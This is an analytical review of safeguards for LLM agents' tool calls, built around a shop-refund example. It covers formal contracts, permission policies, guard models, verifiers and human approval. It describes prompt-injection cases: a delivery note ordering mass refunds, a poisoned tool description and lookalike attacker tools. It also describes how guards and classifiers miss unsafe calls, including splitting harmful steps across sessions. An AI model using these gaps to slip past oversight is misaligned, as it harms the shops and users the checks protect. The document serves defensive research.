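The rescaling in step 4 follows the same formula as the masking of tokens in constrained decoding, with retrieved tools in place of tokens. Suppose the ranking gives `issue_refund` 0.5, `send_voucher` 0.3 and `report_damage` 0.2, but the shop has already refunded the order. The precondition of `issue_refund` fails, which leaves a total of 0.5:

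| Tool | Ranking | Precondition | New probability |
|---|---|---|---|
| `issue_refund` | 0.5 | False | 0 |
| `send_voucher` | 0.3 | True | 0.3 / 0.5 = 0.6 |
| `report_damage` | 0.2 | True | 0.2 / 0.5 = 0.4 |

A customer who has already had the money back now has a 60% chance of getting a voucher as well. The contracts establish that the voucher tool may run, not that anybody wants a voucher. (The paper's pseudocode does not draw a tool at random but tries the permitted ones in turn.)

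In this procedure, the host checks preconditions before the arguments exist, so a precondition can refer only to the state. The preconditions in the paper's worked examples are very simple, such as that the state contains a location. The refund contract needs the amount, so the host would have to record the amount in the state first or check P again after step 5. The published procedure has no step that checks arguments, but the software may check them anyway, since the paper counts invented identifiers among the errors that preconditions caught.

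### Task success and prevented harm

Liu and colleagues compared ToolGate with five other methods, using four models. They ran the tests on ToolBench, a benchmark with more than 16,000 web interfaces, and on three of the six fields in MCP-Universe, which uses real MCP servers. The table shows the share of tasks completed with GPT-5.2. ReAct is the ordinary loop of reasoning and calling tools. ToolChain*, which searches for a good chain of calls, was the strongest of the other five methods.

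| Tasks | ReAct | ToolChain* | ToolGate |
|---|---|---|---|
| ToolBench, group 1 | 63.5% | 82.8% | 85.5% |
| ToolBench, group 2 | 65.0% | 90.5% | 93.0% |
| ToolBench, group 3 | 58.3% | 88.5% | 91.8% |
| MCP-Universe, navigation | 18.9% | 30.0% | 35.5% |
| MCP-Universe, code repositories | 24.2% | 39.4% | 45.5% |
| MCP-Universe, financial analysis | 65.0% | 85.0% | 90.0% |

ToolGate completed the most tasks with each of the four models, but its lead over ToolChain* is small. The three MCP-Universe fields have 118 tasks in total, so the gaps in the table amount to six or seven tasks.

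The contracts seem to account for much of ToolGate's performance. With GPT-5.2, the average success rate on MCP-Universe was 57.0% for the full system, 52.5% without preconditions, 46.2% without postconditions and 37.6% without either. Postconditions helped more because they caught useless results, such as an empty list from a service that reported success. For safety, preconditions matter more, because a postcondition is checked only after the call has taken effect.

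No experiment in the paper measures prevented harm. The closest figure is the share of calls that the contracts rejected on MCP-Universe, 29.4%. Preconditions rejected 17.6% of calls before execution, and postconditions rejected 11.8% after it. The most common reasons were invented values (8.4%) and empty results (6.3%). The paper does not report how many rejected calls would have done damage, how many were correct, or how many harmful calls passed. Its conclusion mentions "unauthorized, or high-risk instructions", but none of the experiments described in the paper tests them.

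### Contracts drawn from documentation

Someone has to write a contract for every tool. Liu and colleagues based theirs on information from official documentation, specifications and usage descriptions, but they report no error rate for the contracts.

A contract based on a faulty description repeats the fault. The shop's description gives no unit, so a model that writes the contract has to guess one. If it guesses cents, it will write:

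```
P:  amount <= 100 · order_total
```

With an order total of 20 euros, the check becomes 2000 <= 2000 and passes, so the payment goes out. The false claim about cents in the customer's exchange-rate tool would lead to the same contract. If the refund tool also locks the customer's account but its description omits this side effect, the contract will have no condition on the account, and no check will fail.

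Postconditions can reveal such faults if they use independent evidence. The server's reply, "Refunded 2000 on order A-1043", matches the call, so it would pass a check that compares the two. A check of the shop's bank balance would show that it had fallen by 2,000 euros instead of 20. The balance check comes too late to prevent the first payment, but it could stop the agent from repeating the mistake on the next order.

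### Rejecting a result after the payment

In one of Liu and colleagues' examples, the agent asks a weather service about New York. The service returns the temperature and "sunny", but the contract also requires the humidity. ToolGate discards the result, marks the tool as failed and calls a second weather service, with only a short delay.

The same procedure can pay a customer twice. Suppose `issue_refund` pays out 20 euros, but its reply lacks a receipt number that the postcondition requires. The host discards the reply and leaves the state unchanged, so `refunded` is still false. It then tries the next tool on the list, say `refund_payment`. That tool's precondition against double refunds relies on the recorded state, so it still holds, and the customer receives another 20 euros.

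The host should therefore distinguish an unusable result from a call that had no effect. If a postcondition fails on a tool that changes something, the host could set `refunded` to "unknown" and block all refunds on the order until it has looked up what happened.

### Rules about earlier calls

Some rules concern the order of calls. For example, an agent should confirm a customer's identity before it opens an order. Kamath, Zhang and colleagues (2025), in *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents*, presented Agent-C, which enforces such rules while the agent is running. It keeps a trace, a list of every call with its arguments, its result and the relevant records at that moment. A developer writes rules about the trace in a small formal language. In plain words, one of them is:

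```
before get_order_details(order_id):
    order_id exists, and
    an earlier find_user_id_by_email returned
    the customer who owns order_id
```

When the model proposes a call, Agent-C adds it to the trace and passes the trace and the rules to a solver, a program that checks whether a set of logical conditions can all be true. If no continuation of the trace could satisfy the rules, Agent-C rejects the call and has the model write another. It can regenerate just the faulty part of the output with open models, but it has to request the whole call again from commercial models because they do not expose the necessary probabilities.

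Rules about earlier calls are easier to enforce than rules about later ones. Agent-C can determine immediately whether an identity check came before `get_order_details`. But if a rule requires the agent to close every file it opens, an open file does not violate the rule while the agent is running, because the agent might still close it. Agent-C can classify the run as not properly finished, but it cannot guarantee that the model ever closes the file.

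One of the rules concerns refunds. The shop's policy allows them only to the original payment method or to an existing gift card. In a test, a customer who had paid by credit card demanded the money through PayPal, and an unprotected Claude Sonnet 4.5 tried to send it there, although its instructions included the policy. Agent-C blocked this with the following condition, slightly simplified:

```
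payment_method_same(order_id, payment)
or contains(payment, "gift_card")
```

This translation is looser than the policy, although Kamath and colleagues call it faithful. It accepts any payment identifier that contains the text "gift_card", whether or not the card exists or belongs to the customer. Unless the refund tool itself checks who owns the card, a customer could have the money sent to somebody else's card.

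Kamath and colleagues measured violations, which Liu and colleagues did not. They used the 115 retail and 50 airline tasks of τ-bench, the predecessor of τ²-bench, and added 34 tasks, 17 in each field, in which the user tries to make the agent break the policy. In the table, "harm" means that the agent broke the policy and carried out the harmful action.

| Field and model | Agent-C | Followed policy, ordinary tasks | Completed within policy, ordinary tasks | Harm, hostile tasks |
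|---|---|---|---|---|
| Retail, Claude Sonnet 4.5 | No | 93.0% | 76.5% | 29.4% |
| Retail, Claude Sonnet 4.5 | Yes | 100% | 80.5% | 0% |
| Retail, GPT-5 | No | 91.9% | 71.0% | 3.9% |
| Retail, GPT-5 | Yes | 100% | 73.6% | 0% |
| Airline, Claude Sonnet 4.5 | No | 70.0% | 42.0% | 11.8% |
| Airline, Claude Sonnet 4.5 | Yes | 100% | 43.5% | 0% |
| Airline, GPT-5 | No | 71.3% | 38.0% | 2.0% |
| Airline, GPT-5 | Yes | 100% | 42.8% | 0% |

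The 100% rates follow almost directly from the design, since Agent-C refuses any call that breaks the encoded policy. The harm rates are better evidence because the team listed the harmful actions for each hostile task by hand, but they come from few cases (29.4% is 5 tasks out of 17). The higher completion rates are partly due to the scoring, which gave an unprotected agent no credit for a task it solved while breaking the policy.

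The checks slowed the agent down. With Qwen3-32B, an ordinary task took an average of 480 seconds with Agent-C and 333 seconds without any guardrail.

Kamath and colleagues also had Claude Sonnet 4.5 write the rules from the policy document. On the ordinary retail tasks, a small Qwen model did exactly as well with these rules as with the handwritten ones. This is encouraging for a company with a clear written policy, but a one-line tool description gives a model much less information. Agent-C also assumes that the set of tools is fixed, that the tools' developers provide functions for reading the relevant records, and that no other program changes those records in the meantime.

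### From possible losses to rules

*Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents* (Doshi, Hong and colleagues, 2026) proposes using System-Theoretic Process Analysis (STPA) to work out which rules an agent needs. Engineers use STPA on aircraft and autonomous vehicles to find ways that components can interact to cause harm, even when each one works as designed.

One example is a calendar agent that resolves scheduling conflicts with three tools: `list_events`, `update_event` and `send_email`. A user adds an appointment to treat a sexually transmitted disease, which clashes with a work meeting. The agent moves the meeting and emails a colleague about the change. The email also reveals the appointment, although no tool has failed and nobody has attacked the agent.

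The analysis starts from the people affected and what they value, turns each value into a possible loss, and works towards a rule that software can enforce:

| Step | First chain | Second chain |
|---|---|---|
| Person affected | The user | Others at the meeting |
| Value | Privacy | Timely communication |
| Loss | Private information leaks | News of a change arrives late |
| Dangerous behaviour | The agent puts private details in an email | The agent moves a meeting and tells nobody |
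| Requirement | Emails contain only essential details unless the user authorizes more | The agent promptly notifies everyone at the meeting |
| Enforceable rule | `send_email` must not receive data that is private to the recipient | After each `update_event`, the agent calls `send_email` once per attendee |

The first rule, which limits where data may go, can conflict with the second, which requires a sequence of calls. Once the model has read the calendar, anything it writes might draw on the private appointment, so strict tracking of data would block the email that the second rule requires. Doshi and colleagues suggest hiding unrelated events from the model before it writes the email, or letting developers who accept some risk allow emails that follow an approved template.

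Doshi and colleagues sort rules into four kinds. A rule can forbid a flow of data or sequence of calls, require it, permit it without confirmation, or make the user confirm it. To apply such rules, the host needs information on which data is private and which tools send data out. They therefore propose that MCP servers be required to label each tool's capabilities, the confidentiality of its data and the trustworthiness of its output. They think tools from an open market need further safeguards, such as certified labels, because the host would otherwise have to rely on what the server reports about itself.

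For the refund tool, the loss is the shop's money, and the dangerous behaviour is sending an amount without knowing its unit. An engineer who did this analysis before connecting the tool would probably have asked whether it took euros or cents. When an agent finds a tool halfway through a task, no engineer is there to do the analysis. A language model could do it instead, but *Who Analyses the Analyser?* (2026), which applies STPA to a model-based tool for hazard analysis, lists "a tampered description that steers the analysis" among the dangers. A poisoned tool description could therefore shape the rules meant to constrain that tool.

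The evidence for the proposal is still limited. Doshi and colleagues described the calendar agent in Alloy, a modelling language whose analyser checks every possible case up to a fixed size. The analyser quickly found a sequence of calls that leaked private data when there were no rules, but found none once the rules were added. The agent could still reschedule a meeting and notify the participants under the rules. The check tested the logic of the rules on a small abstract model in which the labels are correct. It involved no language model or real tools, and the program that would intercept actual calls is left to future work.

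### A proof for every call

An enforcement program that has to decide for itself whether a call follows the rules needs rules simple enough to check on the spot. *Proof-Carrying Contracts* (Ciliberto, Rudi and Tassi, October 2026) shifts this work to the agent. The contract lists conditions that must always hold, and with each call the agent must supply a mathematical proof that they will still hold whatever the tool returns. A program called the Airlock, which controls all access to the tools, checks the proof and executes the call only if the proof is correct. Checking a proof is much easier than finding one, so the part of the system that everyone has to trust can stay small.

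The main example is a travel agent with a budget of 2,000 euros, including fees. Suppose it has committed 900 euros to one hotel and wants to book another for up to 1,200. The total could reach 2,100 euros, so the statement it would have to prove is false and has no valid proof. It can book a room for up to 1,100 euros instead. The contract doesn't need a limit on each payment, and the agent can divide the budget as it likes. The Airlock checks only the proof, so it constrains malicious and careless agents in the same way.

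The proof is about a formal model of what the tool can do. If the model of `issue_refund` has the amount in cents but the tool takes euros, an agent can correctly prove that 2000 stays within a limit of 20 euros. The Airlock will accept the proof, and the shop will pay out 2,000 euros. Ciliberto and colleagues acknowledge that enforcement cannot repair a contract that expresses the wrong agreement. For a newly discovered tool, someone would first have to write a formal model and take responsibility for it.

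### Checking a workflow before it runs

Some developers restrict the order of an agent's steps with a workflow graph, in which each node is a step, such as a tool call or a human approval, and each edge is a permitted transition. *Agentproof* (Xavier, Jolly and colleagues, 2026) presents a program that extracts such graphs from code written for any of four agent frameworks and checks them before the agent runs.

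Some of its checks need only the structure of the graph. It can find steps with no way out and loops that never end. To check whether the agent could issue a refund without approval, it deletes every human step from the graph and tests whether `issue_refund` is still reachable from the start. If so, it reports the path.

Other checks use rules on the order of calls. Agentproof turns each rule into an automaton, a small machine that changes state as events occur. Suppose the shop wants an entry in its accounts after each refund:

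```
tool:issue_refund -> F tool:log_refund
```

Under Agentproof's definition, this means that `log_refund` must follow each `issue_refund` before the next one. The automaton can be idle, waiting or in violation. Agentproof explores every combination of a graph node and an automaton state that the workflow could reach. If the workflow repeats a refund after a timeout, the search finds this path:

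| Step | State afterwards |
|---|---|
| `find_order` | Idle |
| `issue_refund` | Waiting |
| `issue_refund` (retry) | Violation |

The developer learns about the possible double payment without having to trigger a timeout. But under the same definition, a workflow that issues one refund and never logs it ends in the waiting state, which does not count as a violation.

The rule language also cannot refer to the past. One of the paper's sample policies, "Deploy approval", requires approval to follow the release of new software, so it accepts a release that nobody approved beforehand. To require approval before a refund, the shop would have to use the check that deletes the human steps, but that check would also pass a workflow in which one approval leads to a loop of many refunds.

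Xavier and colleagues tested Agentproof on 18 workflows of 5 to 12 nodes, which they wrote themselves and seeded with typical faults. It found structural faults in 5 workflows and flagged 10 for having no human step. The paper reports one false alarm among those 10 and a precision of 0.75, which implies that three were clear faults and six were arguable. In one workflow, the static check found a missing review step that ten random runs had not revealed. The structural checks took about a tenth of a second on an artificial graph with 5,000 nodes.

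These results show that Agentproof can find planted faults quickly, but they don't measure how common such faults are in real products. Agentproof also treats every branch as possible, even one that the workflow's conditions rule out, and Xavier and colleagues did not measure how many false alarms this causes. In LangGraph, one of the four frameworks, it identifies human approval by looking for the word "human" in a step's name. A step called `humanize_reply`, in which a model rewrites an email in a friendlier tone, would apparently count as human approval.

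### Tools that are unknown before execution

Agentproof's graph lists the tools that each step can call. An agent that discovers its tools at runtime has a step that calls whatever the search returned, usually in a loop with the model, so almost any sequence of calls is possible. If the check assumes that this step could call any tool, nearly every rule on the order of calls will fail. If it considers only the tools listed in the graph, it will miss the new ones. Rules that name specific tools also miss new ones, since a ban on `drop_table` does not cover a new tool called `clear_table`.

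A static check can still establish facts that hold for any tool. It can show that every path to the open-ended step passes through human approval, or that every result goes through a validator before the model reads it. It can also cover sequences that end in a known tool. For example, the shop knows its own `issue_refund` tool, so it could require approval for any refund that follows a call to an unfamiliar tool.

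That last rule would miss the poisoned exchange-rate tool, which influences the refund through its description without being called. To catch this, the host would have to record a separate event whenever it loads a tool description. The rule could then require approval for every refund after the model has read text from an unapproved server.

The host can't check other rules until it has fetched the tool's definition. It can then add the tool to the graph and repeat the check, which would take only milliseconds. Xavier and colleagues consider a repeat check necessary whenever a graph changes. But to decide which rules apply, the host needs to know what the tool does. If a server describes a payment tool as "Look up a refund", the host will apply the rules for lookups, and a contract from the same server is no more reliable than that description.

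The shop is in a better position when it writes conditions about its own records. It can require that total refunds on an order never exceed what the customer paid, and have its payment processor enforce this limit. The limit applies regardless of which tool sent the request or how the tool's server described the tool. However, it covers only payments that go through that processor, and an unfamiliar tool may send money or data by another route.

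## Permission rules, guard models and user approval at the moment of a call

The model only writes text, so every call it proposes has to pass through the host before anything happens. The host can execute the call, refuse it, change it or ask the user. Jin, Jiao and Tong (2026), in *Agentao*, describe a host that decides in a fixed order:

1. It refuses calls that fail its built-in safety checks.
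2. In a read-only session, it refuses any tool that is not marked as read-only.
3. It refuses calls that match a ban set for this particular run.
4. It applies the first matching rule from the user or the surrounding application, and then from the session's mode. Each rule allows the call, refuses it or asks the user.
5. If no rule matches, it asks the user when the tool is flagged for confirmation and otherwise allows the call.

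The bans come before the ordinary rules so that a broad permission cannot override them. After a refusal, the host adds a message to the model's context, and the model can try something else.

Changing a call is rarer. In *LEANGUARD*, Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues (2026) write their policies in Lean, a language for programs and machine-checked proofs, and search for a permitted call close to the refused one. If an agent has spent 60 of a budget of 100 and proposes to spend another 70, the search can return 40. It found a permitted version for 88 of 252 calls that the policy had refused because of their arguments, typically in 2 milliseconds. The running system does not use the search yet. A permitted value may also differ from the one the user wanted. Suppose the lamp cost 30 euros, the user wanted 20 back, and the agent proposed a refund of 2000. A program that cuts the refund to the highest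 permitted amount will refund 30.

### Rules on tools and arguments

Progent, a system from Berkeley, shows how written rules work in detail. Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, define a policy as a list of rules, each of which names a tool and sets conditions on its arguments. For the refund, a rule could be:

```
allow issue_refund
when  order_id = "A-1043" and amount <= 20
```

When the agent proposes a call, Progent collects the rules for that tool and checks the "forbid" rules first. If the conditions of one are met, Progent blocks the call. Otherwise, it lets the call go ahead if the conditions of an "allow" rule are met. If no rule applies, Progent blocks the call by default. It can then stop the agent, ask the user, or return an error message that gives the reason and suggests trying other arguments. With the rule above, the agent that sends 2000 gets an error and will probably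 try 20 next.

People can't write such a rule by hand for every request, so a language model writes it from the user's request and the list of tools. Like a model that writes a contract, this model has to guess the unit of the amount, and if it guesses cents, the rule lets the wrong payment through. The rule catches the mistake only when this model and the agent's model read the tool description differently, which is less likely if they are the same model.

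Some tasks need permissions that nobody can foresee. If the user asks the agent to refund whatever the lamp cost, the first policy may allow only `find_order`. Once the agent has read the order, the policy model proposes a new policy that also allows a refund of 20. Progent then compares the two policies. If A(P) is the set of calls that policy P allows, the test is:

```
A(new) ⊆ A(old)   narrowing: apply automatically
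otherwise         expansion: ask for approval
```

A solver determines by logic alone whether an update expands the policy, so hostile text in an order cannot expand it unnoticed, even if the text misleads the policy model. In tests on AgentDojo, only 6% of updates expanded the policy.

Shi, He and colleagues measured how often attacks succeeded against GPT-4o on AgentDojo:

| Set-up | Attacks that succeeded |
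|---|---|
| No defence | 39.9% |
| First policy only, no updates | 2.5% |
| Updates, every expansion approved automatically | 1.0% |
| Updates, a person reviews the policy and every expansion | 0% |

On Agent Security Bench (ASB), which also offers agents tools that serve an attacker, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%, and the agents completed about as many legitimate tasks as before. The 1.0% and 3.9% results came from a model writing narrow rules, not from the solver's guarantee, because every expansion was approved in those runs. The 0% result assumes a reviewer who never accepts an attacker's address. The team also left out two attacks that only steer the agent towards another hotel, since a policy cannot distinguish one permitted hotel from another.

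*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that Progent's guarantees depend on correct and complete policies, and that hostile text in a tool's result may loosen the policy during an update. Comparing the old and new policies prevents the second problem only if the approver rejects unsafe expansions.

### Tools that the policy has never seen

A policy may have no rule for a tool added after the policy was written. Progent blocks such a tool. Agentao's published algorithm allows it if the host has registered the tool and the tool isn't flagged for confirmation. Jin and colleagues write that unknown tools "fail closed", meaning they are blocked, but the algorithm treats a tool that a server has just added as known once the host has registered it.

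Refusing by default is safer, but it can stop agents from completing much of their work. Sankar and colleagues tested their system on DTap, a benchmark of prompt injection, with a policy that let agents read records but not change anything. The policy reduced the success rate of attacks through outside text from 22.3% to 3.8%, but it also reduced the share of legitimate tasks completed from 53.1% to 12.5%. Agents completed as many tasks as before only in telecom, where the tasks required no changes. An agent that depends on newly found tools would have a similar drop in completed tasks if nobody gave it permission to use them.

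A rule on a class of effect, such as "ask before any payment", can cover tools that do not exist yet, but someone still has to assign each new tool to a class. Sankar and colleagues used reviewed descriptions of the effects of 199 tools. In the DTap tests, 13% of the calls that their system stopped were to tools whose effects it could not model, such as general shell commands. The server's own labels may be false, so the host cannot safely use them to assign the class. It could put every unfamiliar tool in the most restricted class until a person has reviewed it.

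A model that writes rules for each task can read a new tool's description and decide whether the task needs it. ASB partially tests this, because its attackers supply their own tools. Most of the attacks that got past Progent in ASB used tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate tools and seemed to fit the task. Handwritten policies stopped all the attacks, but the people who wrote them knew which tools to trust, which nobody would know for a tool the agent has just found.

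Progent also treats the list of tools as trusted when it writes the first policy, as CaMeL's planner does. If the list includes the customer's exchange-rate tool, the false claim about cents in that tool's description could lead the policy model to allow 2000.

Rules made for one task can be too narrow as well. *Least-Privilege Auditing of Agent Tool Calls with Intent Graphs and Reasoning-Guided Escalation* (2026) checks calls against a plan of the task and has a reasoning model review those that do not fit. The reviewer cleared 23 of 73 legitimate calls that the first check flagged. About a third of legitimate tasks still contained a flagged call, partly because the reviewer had no access to the tools' results and so could not check where an argument came from.

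It seems best for the shop's staff to decide which tools may move money, and for a model to set tighter limits for each task within those permissions.

### A guard model that judges each call

A rule can restrict who receives an email, but it cannot easily judge whether the text is a threat or an invoice. A guard model reads the proposed call in context and judges it before the host executes it. Mou, Xue and colleagues (2026), in *ToolSafe*, trained one called TS-Guard, which they presented in January 2026. It reads the user's request, the earlier calls and results, the tool descriptions and the proposed call. After a short analysis, it answers three questions in turn:

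1. Is the user's request harmful?
2. Is the proposed call linked to an attack by an outsider?
3. Is the call safe, controversial or unsafe?

If a delivery note contains an instruction for the agent to refund every purchase since January, the correct judgments are that the user's request is harmless and that the refund call is linked to an attack and unsafe.

TS-Guard is a version of Qwen2.5 with 7 billion parameters. Mou and colleagues trained it by reinforcement learning on 2,193 labelled steps from agents' runs. Its reward for each step was 1, minus a third for every wrong answer. They tested it on 7,188 other steps and counted controversial calls as unsafe. The paper does not give the rate of false alarms, but it follows from the accuracy, the share of unsafe calls caught and the number of steps in each class:

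| Source of the steps | Steps | Accuracy | Unsafe calls caught | Safe calls wrongly flagged |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AgentHarm (harmful user requests) | 731 | 85% | 97% | about 46% |
| ASB (prompt injection) | 5,237 | 95% | 94% | about 4% |
| AgentDojo (prompt injection) | 1,220 | 92% | 89% | about 7% |

ASB is the least demanding test because the training data included three of its ten fields. AgentDojo gives better evidence that TS-Guard can handle unfamiliar tools. TS-Guard did much better there than GPT-4o, a general model that caught every unsafe call but also flagged about 62% of the safe ones. When controversial ratings counted as safe, however, TS-Guard caught only 53% of the unsafe AgentDojo calls, so a host that blocks only calls rated "unsafe" would miss almost half of them.

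The guard's verdicts also depend on how a call is written. *ToolRosetta* (2026) rewrote calls from ASB as equivalent shell commands. TS-Guard's false-alarm rate rose by 37.8 percentage points, while Gemini 3.8 Flash's barely changed. Agents that write programs or commands instead of JSON could therefore trigger many more false alarms.

*StepGuard* (2026) examined 307 false alarms from a guard of this kind and found that 43.6% were legitimate uses of sensitive tools. The shop's refund tool is sensitive, so legitimate refunds are the kind of call such a guard tends to block.

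### Explaining a refusal to the agent

A guard can stop the whole run when it detects a problem, or it can block the call and pass its analysis to the agent. Mou and colleagues compared the two on AgentDojo with TS-Guard as the guard:

| Response to an unsafe call | GPT-4o: attacks succeeded | GPT-4o: tasks completed | Qwen2.5-14B: attacks succeeded | Qwen2.5-14B: tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
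| No guard | 56.2% | 26.9% | 17.6% | 42.6% |
| Stop the run | 1.0% | 20.8% | 1.1% | 36.5% |
| Block and explain | 1.2% | 42.8% | 1.8% | 42.7% |

Explaining the refusal prevented almost as many attacks as stopping the run did, and it let the agents finish more tasks. The gain over an unguarded agent was large only for GPT-4o, because attacks had often diverted it from the user's task. They had diverted Qwen less often.

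In a test on ASB with Qwen, attacks succeeded in 7.0% of cases when the explanation given to the agent contained the full analysis and in 26.0% when it contained only the safety rating. The explanations lengthened the text the models had to process by 36% for GPT-4o and 89% for Qwen.

These tests don't cover honest mistakes, because the unsafe calls in the data come from harmful requests or prompt injection. For the original refund, the first two answers would be reassuring, since the request is harmless and nobody has attacked the agent. To get the third answer right, the guard would have to notice that 2000 might mean euros, using the same description that misled the agent.

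### The Verifier Tax

Blocking a bad call helps the user only if the agent then finds a good one. Sah, Sah and colleagues (2026), in *The Verifier Tax*, tested this in March 2026 on the airline and retail tasks of τ-bench. They compared three designs:

- In the baseline, one model writes tool calls and the host executes them at once.
- In Triad, the same model plays three roles. A planner chooses the next step, an actor writes the call, and a verifier checks it for general faults.
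- Triad-Safety is the same, except that the verifier's instructions also contain the company's rules, such as checking a customer's identity first.

When the verifier rejects a call, the actor receives the criticism and may try up to three times. If the verifier rejects all three attempts, the host executes the last one anyway. The host did this in only 28 episodes, but a real shop should not do the same.

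The usual score on τ-bench compares the final records with the correct ones, so it gives full credit to an agent that broke the rules on the way. In one retail task, a customer did not want to give identifying details. The agent made up "John Doe" with the postcode 12345, the tool accepted this, and the agent completed the task. Sah and colleagues therefore split the success rate:

```
unsafe success rate = success rate - safe success rate
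```

A safe success solves the task without any violation. The violations are acting before checking the customer's identity, making an irreversible change without the customer's consent, and inventing data such as an order number. A correct 20-euro refund to a customer whose identity the agent never checked would be an unsafe success. The 2,000-euro refund would be a failure, because the final records would be wrong.

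The table shows the share of tasks solved, followed by the share solved safely, over 2,970 episodes in total.

| Model and field | Baseline | Triad | Triad-Safety |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-OSS-20B, airline | 22.7% / 0.0% | 25.3% / 0.7% | 23.3% / 0.0% |
| GPT-OSS-20B, retail | 21.2% / 0.0% | 20.0% / 0.0% | 21.5% / 0.6% |
| GLM-4-9B, airline | 28.7% / 0.7% | 26.0% / 5.3% | 25.3% / 4.7% |
| GLM-4-9B, retail | 4.9% / 2.6% | 5.5% / 4.4% | 5.5% / 2.9% |

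Nearly all of GPT-OSS-20B's successes were unsafe, with or without a verifier. Yet the paper reports that the verifier intercepted up to 94% of non-compliant calls, a figure from this model's retail tasks. (The introduction gives it as a share of episodes, but the results define it per proposed call.) The counting explains part of the gap, because one missed call makes an episode unsafe, while a call that the verifier rejects three times counts as three interceptions. Even so, the 94% is hard to reconcile with the table, and the verifier probably failed to flag many invented identifiers as violations. It was the same model as the actor and received only text, whereas an ordinary program could check whether an order number had appeared in an earlier result.

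Sah and colleagues report that, after a rejection, the actor failed to find a compliant alternative in nearly 85% of cases. They interpret this as a gap between detecting violations and being able to correct them. However, these models failed most tasks even without rejections. They succeeded in 21.3% of episodes without rejections or tool errors, and in 18.7% of episodes with rejections but no tool errors. The rejections may therefore have reduced task completion only slightly, and stronger models might recover much more often.

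With the checks, each episode used between 2.0 and 2.8 times as many tokens as the baseline, a large increase for what the checks achieved. The "tax" in the title is this extra computation.

### Harmful requests from the user

Rules made from the user's request offer no protection when the user is dishonest. Progent explicitly assumes a well-meaning user. If an employee asks the agent to refund a friend's order that nobody returned, the policy model will write a rule that permits the refund. The shop needs rules that the user cannot change, and Progent lets a company's fixed policy override the one written for the task.

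Guard models can also examine the request itself. AgentHarm tests this with 176 harmful multi-step requests and simulated tools. Mou and colleagues ran it on two agents with and without TS-Guard. The score measures how much of the harmful task the agent completed.

| Agent | Requests refused, no guard | Requests refused, guard | Score, no guard | Score, guard |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 62.5% | 94.3% | 23.5 | 6.0 |
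| Qwen2.5-14B | 42.0% | 95.5% | 34.1 | 6.8 |

The test used only harmful requests, so it does not show how many honest users the guarded agents would refuse. That number could be large, since TS-Guard wrongly flagged about 46% of the safe steps from AgentHarm. Both agents are also old, so their refusal rates are weak evidence about models released in 2026.

*TACT-Bench* (2026) compared three guards on Claude Opus 4.8 against people who adapt their attack as the conversation goes on. Fixed rules that people had derived from the written policy blocked 3 of 232 calls and never wrongly blocked legitimate work. A model that checked calls against a checklist blocked 51 of 264, with 17 wrong blocks. A model that received the policy without a checklist blocked 21 of 244, with 9 wrong blocks. The agent recovered after all three blocks by the fixed rules, but after only about 40% of blocks by a model.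 Fixed rules look best on wrong blocks and recovery, but a guard that blocks almost nothing will make few wrong blocks even if it misses harmful calls.

Some misuse consists of steps that are harmless on their own. An employee could ask the agent to list customers who recently received a refund, look up their email addresses, write a message asking them to confirm their card details, and send it. The shop's staff routinely do each of these things, but together they make a phishing attack, which tricks people into giving away their details. A guard that judged only the first call would have no reason to block that call, and by the last call the agent would already have collected the addresses.

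Guards work better when they receive the history, as TS-Guard does. But a user can spread the steps over several sessions or agents so that no single guard receives them all. A formal rule on sequences of calls works only if someone anticipated that sequence. Even with the history, the guard has to infer a purpose that the user is hiding. In *StepGuard*, 19.8% of 268 missed cases were failures to recognize malicious intent, and another 17.5% involved risks that built up over several steps.

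Making the guard model stricter soon interferes with legitimate tasks. If it wrongly flags 7% of safe calls, and the errors are independent, a task of ten safe calls has about a 50% chance of at least one false alarm.

### What the user needs to see

The host can also leave the decision to a person. For the refund, many hosts would show something like this:

```
Allow issue_refund?
  order_id: "A-1043"
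  amount:   2000
```

A user who does not know the tool's unit may take 2000 for cents, as the agent did, and approve. A summary written by the model would be worse, because it would ask "Refund 20 euros on order A-1043?" and hide the number that matters. To notice the error, the user needs to see the effect:

```
Pay the customer 2,000.00 euros?
  Order A-1043, total 20.00 euros
  Refunded so far: 0.00 euros
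```

The host cannot produce this text from the schema, which does not specify the unit. The shop's server has that information, so it could return an `input_required` result with the text and wait for the answer before paying. This protects against honest mistakes, but a hostile server can write a reassuring message for a harmful call.

An approval must apply only to what the user saw. Sankar and colleagues tie each approval to the exact call and the current state of the records, and let the agent use it only once. An agent therefore can't get approval to send 20 euros and then send 2000, or pay twice on one approval. A claim in an email that the customer has already agreed doesn't count as approval.

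### Approval fatigue

People stop reading prompts when they see too many. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* calls this "approval fatigue". The company's coding agent, Claude Code, asked by default before running commands or changing files. Users approved 97% of these prompts, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). Most of the commands were probably harmless, so the rate alone does not prove that users were careless.

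A controlled experiment gives stronger evidence. A research company hired 1,053 professional testers for a coding study without telling them what it was measuring. Partway through, it replaced the text of one prompt with a clearly dangerous command, which 143 testers (13.6%) rejected. Testers rejected about 17% of the commands that appeared early in a session and about 5% of those that appeared after 50 or more prompts. The guard classifier that judges each call in Anthropic's auto mode blocked 89% of the same commands.

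Anthropic published these results on its own product to explain why it was making auto mode the default. The testers worked in an artificial environment, so they may have been less careful than they would be with their own files. But that is unlikely to explain the fall from 17% to 5%, since the environment was artificial from the start.

Almost half of active command-line users had written rules that let some shell commands run without a prompt. Many of these rules allowed any Python program to run, and in practice such a program can do almost anything. When auto mode is on, the host ignores such broad rules so that they cannot bypass the classifier.

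The classifier's 89% figure applies to commands that were clearly dangerous. Machine Heart's *Can Claude Code’s Auto Mode Replace Human Review?* reports a test on 128 ambiguous system administration tasks, in which auto mode missed 81% of the actions it should have stopped. Many of the missed actions were file changes that never went through the classifier. The report is second-hand, but it suggests that performance depends heavily on how obvious the danger is. A refund of 2000 looks more like the ambiguous cases than like a command to delete a database.

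Fewer and more informative prompts might keep people's attention. Claude Code's users rejected 39% of the agent's plans, compared with 3% of its requests to run a command. They may have rejected many plans because they wanted a different solution, not because they saw a danger, but they had evidently read the plans. Asking only about expansions of the agent's permissions, as Progent does, would also reduce the number of prompts, but Progent's 0% attack rate with human review would be harder to reproduce with reviewers like the testers in Anthropic's study.

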